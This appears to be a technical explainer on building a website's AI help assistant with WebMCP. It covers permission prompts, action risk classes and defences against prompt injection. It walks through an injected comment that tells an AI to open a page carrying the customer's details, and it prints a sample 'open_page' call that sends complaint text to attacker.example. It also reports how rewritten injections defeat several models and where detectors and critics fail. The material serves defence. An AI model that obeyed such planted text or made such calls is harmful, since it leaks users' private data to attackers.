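ChatGPT asks for permission before it starts to interact with a website, and again before sensitive steps such as making purchases, deleting data, sending messages, sharing personal information and changing account permissions. Before it shares sensitive information, it explains what it will send, where and why. It asks immediately before sending, even if the user has already approved the website or the task. If a site's tool requests information from outside the current page, ChatGPT asks the user to verify the request. Users can turn off site tools completely under Permissions in the browser settings.

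The help site could keep the two questions separate in the same way. A customer who has allowed the assistant to work on the page hasn't yet agreed to send anything.

A customer who has just told ChatGPT "yes, buy it" will probably click away the shop's own confirmation dialog. The group behind WebMCP was already discussing how to avoid such double prompts in December 2025, according to W3C (2025). But the site can't rely on the agent to ask, because the next visitor's agent may not. For purchases, an occasional duplicate prompt is a less serious mistake than no prompt at all.

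WebMCP's own way to ask the user was a function called `requestUserInteraction`. In Walderman and colleagues' 2025 example, a `buyProduct` handler calls it to show a dialog and stops with an error if the user cancels. The page draws the dialog and collects the answer. Brandon Walderman explained at the May meeting that the agent doesn't need information about the dialog and just gets the final result.

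The function can delay the tool's purchase until the user answers. But an agent that also clicks can use the shop's ordinary Buy button without calling the tool, or it may press "OK" in the dialog itself. At the same meeting, Benjamin VanderSloot said the group should try to guarantee that the user always sees the question, and pointed out that an abusive site could bombard people with questions.

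It is also unclear how long the function will last. In June, Walderman proposed replacing it with `requestUserInput`, which has three modes (W3C, *WebML CG Teleconference*, minutes of 11 June 2026). In "interactive" mode, the user answers on the page. In "form" mode, the agent shows a form and passes on the answers. In "url" mode, the user opens a separate address, which keeps passwords away from the agent. The last two are for when the page runs on a remote server and the user is, for example, in a chat app on a phone. The group agreed to specify the interactive mode first. On 1 September, Chrome for Developers still listed `requestUserInteraction()` as part of the draft.

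Developers who use either function should check that it exists before the handler does anything else. If it is missing, the handler has to refuse, because code that skips the question would complete the purchase without asking.

### Rules for the help site

The table applies this to the help site's own assistant. The classes are judgements, and the registry and its reviewer agreed on judgements of this kind only half the time, so another developer could reasonably classify some actions differently.

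| Action | Class | What the assistant may do | Condition |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scroll | R1 | Act | Not while the customer is typing; show a way back |
| Change the theme for this visit | R1 | Act | Save the old value and show Undo |
| Open another article | R1 with a saved draft, R4 without | Act, or offer a link | Read the saved draft back before leaving |
| Fill in a field | R1 | Act if the field is empty, ask before replacing text | Never passwords or card numbers |
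| Submit the complaint | R4 | Nothing; the customer presses Submit | The server rejects duplicates |
| Change account settings | R1 for language, R3 for email address, password or access | Ask about the language, nothing for the rest | The server checks the user's role |
| Buy | R2 with a known refund, R4 without | Fill the cart; the customer pays | The server checks the price |
| Delete | R1 if the site keeps a copy, R4 if not | Ask if there is a copy, otherwise nothing | The question names the item |

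Filling in a field is R1 only if nothing happens until the customer submits the form. Some forms save or send as soon as a value changes, so the assistant would submit data just by filling in a field. The developers have to check each form for this before they give the assistant the tool.

Confirmation questions for deletion need the most careful wording. "Delete my complaint" could mean the half-written text in the box or the case that staff opened last week, and the user would answer "yes" to "Are you sure?" either way. The question should show the first line of the text or the case number, and the button should read "Delete draft" or "Delete case 4821".

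## Instructions hidden in page content

The assistant also reads text written by people other than the customer. Suppose readers of the help site can comment under each article, and the customer, partway through writing the complaint, asks, "Do other people say how long refunds take?" A tool called `read_comments` returns the ten newest comments. Nine are about refunds, and the tenth contains an instruction for any AI assistant that reads it to open a certain web page and add the customer's details to the page's address.

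If the model obeys, the attacker has carried out a *prompt injection*, in which the model wrongly treats text from a source other than the user as an instruction. The attacker doesn't need access to the customer's account or computer. Posting a comment, product review or support ticket is enough.

### Why a model may obey a comment

Chrome for Developers (2026) explains in its guidance for agent developers that a language model processes instructions and data as a single sequence of tokens. The developers' instructions, the customer's question and the ten comments are all part of that sequence. Software can mark where each part begins, and AI companies train their models to give a tool's output less authority than the user's request. But this training only gives the model a tendency, which a cleverly worded comment can overcome.

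Websites solved a similar problem with comments long ago. Before displaying a comment, a site converts the characters that would start an HTML tag, so the browser shows the comment as text instead of running it as code. Language models have no equivalent of this conversion. Deleting everything that looks like an instruction wouldn't work either, because help articles consist largely of instructions. For example, the assistant should repeat "Press Submit when you have finished" to the customer, not press the button itself.

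### How mild actions cause harm

Suppose the site has a tool, `open_page`, that accepts any address. Following the comment, the model could call it like this:

```
open_page   {"url": "https://attacker.example/?note=charged+twice+in+March"}
```

To load the page, the browser sends this address, including the note, to the attacker's server. The customer sees an unfamiliar page and presses Back, which may bring back the complaint, but the attacker still has the note. Anything in the conversation can leak this way, so a tool that seems only to open pages can disclose information irreversibly.

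The leak can happen without a visible page. If a tool such as CopilotKit's background example loads an image from another website, the browser sends the same kind of request. If the chat panel displays images in the assistant's replies, the model can cause the leak without calling a tool.

Scrolling and highlighting send no data out, but they can make a fraud look as if the company endorses it. A comment might contain a "Claim your refund" button that leads to a fake login page. Most customers would scroll past it, but if the site's own assistant scrolls to the button and highlights it, they have good reason to think the company recommends it.

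The short list of section names in `scroll_to` prevents this only if attackers can't add names to it. The page builds the list from its headings, so if comments can contain headings, an attacker's heading can end up on it. The code should collect headings only from the article itself, and the highlighting tool should accept only passages from the article.

A style change can hide a warning that would have exposed a fraud. Suppose the site displays "We never ask for your password in the comments" above the comments. A tool that sets any colour can make this warning the same colour as its background. The `set_theme` tool can't do this if the warning is readable in all three of its themes. Undo would bring the warning back, but by then the customer may have typed their password into a fake page.

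### How often attacks succeed

How often an injection succeeds depends heavily on how hard the attacker tries. In October 2026, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *BrowseSafe++*, tested seven models on 1,024 tasks with injections that came mostly from real web pages. With their original wording, the injections reached their goal in only 0.49 to 4.00% of tasks. The researchers then had other models study each failure and rewrite the injection, for up to 64 attempts per task. The table gives rounded results for five of the seven models:

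| Model | Original wording | After rewriting | Rewritten, goal is a false answer | Rewritten, goal is to change something |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 2.1% | 31% | 41% | 8% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.5% | 65% | 81% | 29% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.6% | 79% | 86% | 59% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 2.9% | 93% | 97% | 84% |
| Kimi K2 | 0.6% | 95% | 97% | 91% |

On 284 of the tasks, the attacks succeeded against all seven models, so replacing one model with another would not have protected those users.

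The rewriting process had access to what the agent did at each step, which a real attacker may lack. Someone testing comments on the help site would see only the assistant's replies and the changes on the page. But anyone can open the site's chatbot and keep trying, and a comment that works once may then work on many customers. Chen and colleagues did not run the rewritten attacks against the newest models in their paper, such as GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5.

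Less persistent attacks can fail completely. In *Domain-Conditioned Safety in Frontier Computer-Using Agents* (2026), hand-written injections never succeeded against Claude Sonnet 4.6 or GPT-5.4 in 16 attempts each. This count excludes a bank task on which each model stopped working once. The sample is small, and even if the true success rate were 17%, all 16 attempts would fail about one time in twenty.

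The researchers also varied the developers' instructions to the model. One version told it to follow any notices on the page, and another warned that all page content was untrusted. Sonnet 4.6 resisted the attacks under every version, so the researchers attribute its resistance to training. But because no attack succeeded, the experiment can't show whether a warning helps against stronger attacks.

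A more capable model isn't always safer. *INFUSE* (2026), a test of many kinds of agent, judged an average of 19.6% of attack runs successful. The rate was 26.3% for GPT-5, 12.6% for the newer GPT-5.4, and 8.4% for GPT-5-Nano, a much smaller model.

### Limiting where data can go

The help site can remove most of the ways for data to leave, though it can't make its model immune to injected instructions. `open_article` accepts only article names, so the model can't put the complaint in a web address. At worst, an injected comment makes the assistant open the wrong article.

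Even a fixed list lets a little information through if it includes outside websites, because the choice of page can be a signal. One choice among 40 pages conveys at most log₂ 40 bits, or about 5.3. A 16-digit card number takes about 53 bits, so the assistant would have to open ten pages to leak one, and the attacker would need the visitor records of all of them. This is a minor risk compared with a tool that accepts any address.

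A more serious gap is that the model can write a link in its reply. Showing the customer the full address helps only if they read it, and few people will read a 300-character address. The chat panel should make a link clickable only if its address is on the site's list, and should treat images the same way.

Browsers can enforce part of this. An *origin* is the protocol, host name and port that together identify a site, such as `https://help.example`. A site can use a *Content Security Policy* to tell the browser which origins its pages may load images from and its scripts may contact. The policy would block the leak through the background image even if the developers forgot to restrict the tool. It doesn't control which pages the user's tab can open, so data would still leak through `open_page`.

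Chrome for Developers recommends limiting a browser agent to the origins relevant to the user's task. This limit doesn't prevent harm within a single origin. The help site's comments and account pages share an origin, so an injected instruction could make an agent post the customer's details as a public comment, where the attacker could read them.

A wider problem is that an agent can carry text from one site to another. Browsers normally stop one site's code from reading another site's pages, but an agent can read both. The WebMCP group's *security privacy questionnaire* raises this risk under the question of what the form should have asked. The matching section of the draft was still marked "TODO".

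Data can also leak without an attacker. Brave's *Privacy risks of agentic oversharing on the Web* notes that outside services and analytics systems can see an agent's searches, clicks, page visits and submitted forms. If the help site's search puts the customer's words in the page's address, a company that measures the site's traffic may receive them too.

### A replay of recorded attacks

*Can You Undo It?* tests a rule that combines a list of allowed destinations with a record of what the agent has read. Once an agent has read any data, the software treats every call that could send data out as irreversible and asks the user about it, unless all of the call's destinations are on the list.

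The researchers applied this *session guard* to 2,158 recorded runs from two existing tests of agents. They counted the calls at which the guard would have stopped to ask under each rule, without running the agents again.

Of the 949 runs that contained an injection, 47 ended with the attacker's goal met. In 29 of these, the researchers could tie the attack to a particular call. The table shows how many of those 29 calls each rule would have caught, and how often it would have asked in the 1,209 harmless runs:

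| Rule | Attack calls that trigger a question | Questions in harmless runs |
|---|---|---|
| Ask only about high-severity calls | 9 of 29 | 1,087 |
| Ask about calls that write, not calls that read | 18 of 29 | 1,895 |
| Session guard | 29 of 29 | 1,904 |
| Session guard, counting web requests as ordinary reads | 18 of 29 | 1,891 |
| Count every web request as irreversible | 29 of 29 | 1,911 |

The read/write rule misses 11 calls because fetching a web page looks like reading, even though the address can carry data out. The session guard catches them and asks only nine more questions. Its whole advantage depends on counting a web request as a possible disclosure. Without that assumption, it also catches only 18. The memory adds much less, since a cruder rule that counts every web request as irreversible also catches all 29, with seven more questions in the harmless runs.

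The guard may not prevent every attack, even though it scored 29 out of 29. That score leaves out 18 successful attacks that the researchers couldn't tie to one call, and a user may approve the call anyway. All the runs used one older model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet. Newer models may fall for different injections and use other tools, though an address can carry data out whichever model writes it.

The help site can use the same idea. The customer's complaint is already in the conversation, so the risk rises when the assistant reads a stranger's text. The `read_comments` handler can record this in session storage before it returns anything, and `gate` can call this function instead of `policy.get`:

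```js
const canSend = new Set(["post_comment", "open_outside_page"]);

function ruleFor(name) {
  const rule = policy.get(name);
  const exposed = sessionStorage.getItem("read-comments") === "yes";
  return rule && exposed && canSend.has(name) ? "ask" : rule;
}
```

The comments stay in the model's input for the rest of the conversation, so the site should clear this record only when a new conversation starts.

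### Hints and length limits

WebMCP lets a tool's author warn the agent that the tool's output may contain untrusted text. Chrome for Developers advises adding `untrustedContentHint` to any tool that returns content from users or outside sources. The agent's software can then *spotlight* the output, which means marking it off and telling the model to treat it as data.

One way to mark page text as data is to put it between special tags, but an attacker who guesses the closing tag can include it in a comment. Encoding the text in Base64, which uses only letters, digits and a few symbols, prevents this but makes the text about a third longer. Both methods still rely on the model following the instruction to treat the text as data, and an injection tries to make the model ignore that instruction.

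Like other tool hints, this one depends on the developer's honesty, and even an honest developer can apply it too broadly. If one tool returned both the refund rules and the comments, the hint would also cover the company's own text. With separate tools, the help site can label only the comments.

By default, other websites can't see a page's tools, but a developer can use the `exposedTo` option to list trusted origins that may use a tool when one site embeds the other. Chrome for Developers warns that even a read-only tool, such as one that returns a user's favourite products, reveals something about the user. The option doesn't protect against instructions injected in a comment, because an agent that already has access to the tool can send its result elsewhere.

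Chrome for Developers also recommends length limits:

| Text | Recommended maximum |
|---|---|
| Tool description | 500 characters |
| Parameter description | 150 characters |
| Tool or parameter name | 30 characters |
| Output of one tool | 1,500 characters |

Short texts give an attacker less room for repetition and elaborate persuasion, but 1,500 characters, or about 250 words, is plenty for an injection. An attacker can also use the limit just to disrupt the agent. Chrome advises agent builders to reject outputs that are too long, so one very long comment could make an agent discard the other nine. The `read_comments` handler should therefore shorten each comment separately.

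### Detectors and checking models

A *detector* is a model that checks text for injections before it reaches the assistant. Chen and colleagues tested several general-purpose models as detectors. GPT-6 Astra did best overall but flagged 14 to 15% of harmless pages. Claude Opus 5.5 flagged only 4 to 5% but missed roughly a fifth of the attacks. A small detector that the researchers trained themselves was more accurate than any of the general-purpose models, and flagged 1.35 to 7.40% of harmless pages, depending on the page format. Its test pages came from the same collection as its training pages, so it may do worse on other pages.

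A model that recognises an injection may still follow it. Chen and colleagues asked each model to check a page for injections and, separately, to carry out a task on the same page. In 74% of the cases where a model followed an injection, it had flagged that injection in the other test. The help site therefore can't rely on the assistant to check what it reads, and needs a separate step that withholds injected text from it.

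A checking model, or *critic*, reviews each proposed call against the user's request, usually without receiving the untrusted text, so the comment can't influence it directly. On the help site, the user asked "Do other people say how long refunds take?", so the critic would refuse a call that opens an unknown website. It can also refuse calls that pass on more personal data than the tool needs. With OpenAI's site tools, ChatGPT does a similar check before each call, reviewing the tool and the information it would receive.

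The critic has blind spots too:

- The customer may delegate the decision, as in "Do whatever the top comment says to fix my login." Without the comment, the critic can't tell a sensible fix from a harmful one.
- A free-text argument can carry the attacker's words to the critic. Arguments from a fixed list can't.
- The critic sees only tool calls, so an injected comment can still change what the assistant tells the customer.

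False answers matter because they were the main weakness of Sonnet 5, the model that best resisted the rewritten attacks. Attackers got it to give a false answer about five times as often as they got it to change something. On the help site, a false answer could be a fraudster's phone number. The site's code can remove any phone number from a reply unless the number appears on the company's contact page.

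### Risks in the WebMCP group's analysis

In November 2025, Huang (2025), in *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP*, set out three risks for the group that drafts the interface.

The first is prompt injection, which can enter through a tool's description, its output, or the input an agent gives it. Input is a risk if the site runs its own model. For example, the company might use one to summarise complaints for its staff, and a fraudster could write a complaint containing instructions for that model. According to W3C's *webmachinelearning minutes* (2025), Huang wasn't sure that this scenario belonged in WebMCP's analysis, because the site runs the model. The company still has to deal with it, and the safest design gives the summarising model no tools that can change a case.

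A tool can also misstate what it does, on purpose or by accident. Huang's example is a shop's `finalizeCart` tool, which could show the cart or complete the purchase. If it completes the purchase when the user only wanted to see the cart, it is unclear whether the agent or the shop is to blame. Huang notes in his slides that this isn't really a security concern, but it becomes one when a site misleads agents deliberately. *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026) found that a tool's name, description and hints influence, to varying degrees, which tool an agent picks.

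Huang also warns about tools that request too much personal data. A dress shop's search tool needs a size and a price. If its schema also has fields for age, location and pregnancy, an agent that has stored these details about its user may fill them in, and the shop can then profile a user who never gave their name. According to the questionnaire, tools outside WebMCP can do the same.

The group hasn't settled who should guard against these risks. The Decoder's *Google's WebMCP moves the web closer to becoming a structured database* reports a Google developer's view that each agent, not the interface, is responsible for protecting against prompt injection. According to the questionnaire, the specification had no binding guidance on the misuse of tools for sensitive operations such as purchases.

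Chromestatus (2026) announced the first developer tests of WebMCP in February, in *Ready for Developer Testing*. Tom Jones objected on the mailing list that there had been no security review. Johann Hofmann of the Chrome team replied that the work was under way and that this was an early prototype. In W3C TAG's *Incubation*, informal notes from the W3C group that reviews new web features, one member predicted that people would exploit WebMCP. By 20 August, according to W3C, neither that group nor W3C's privacy reviewers had given a formal response, and the analysis of possible attacks was still a draft.
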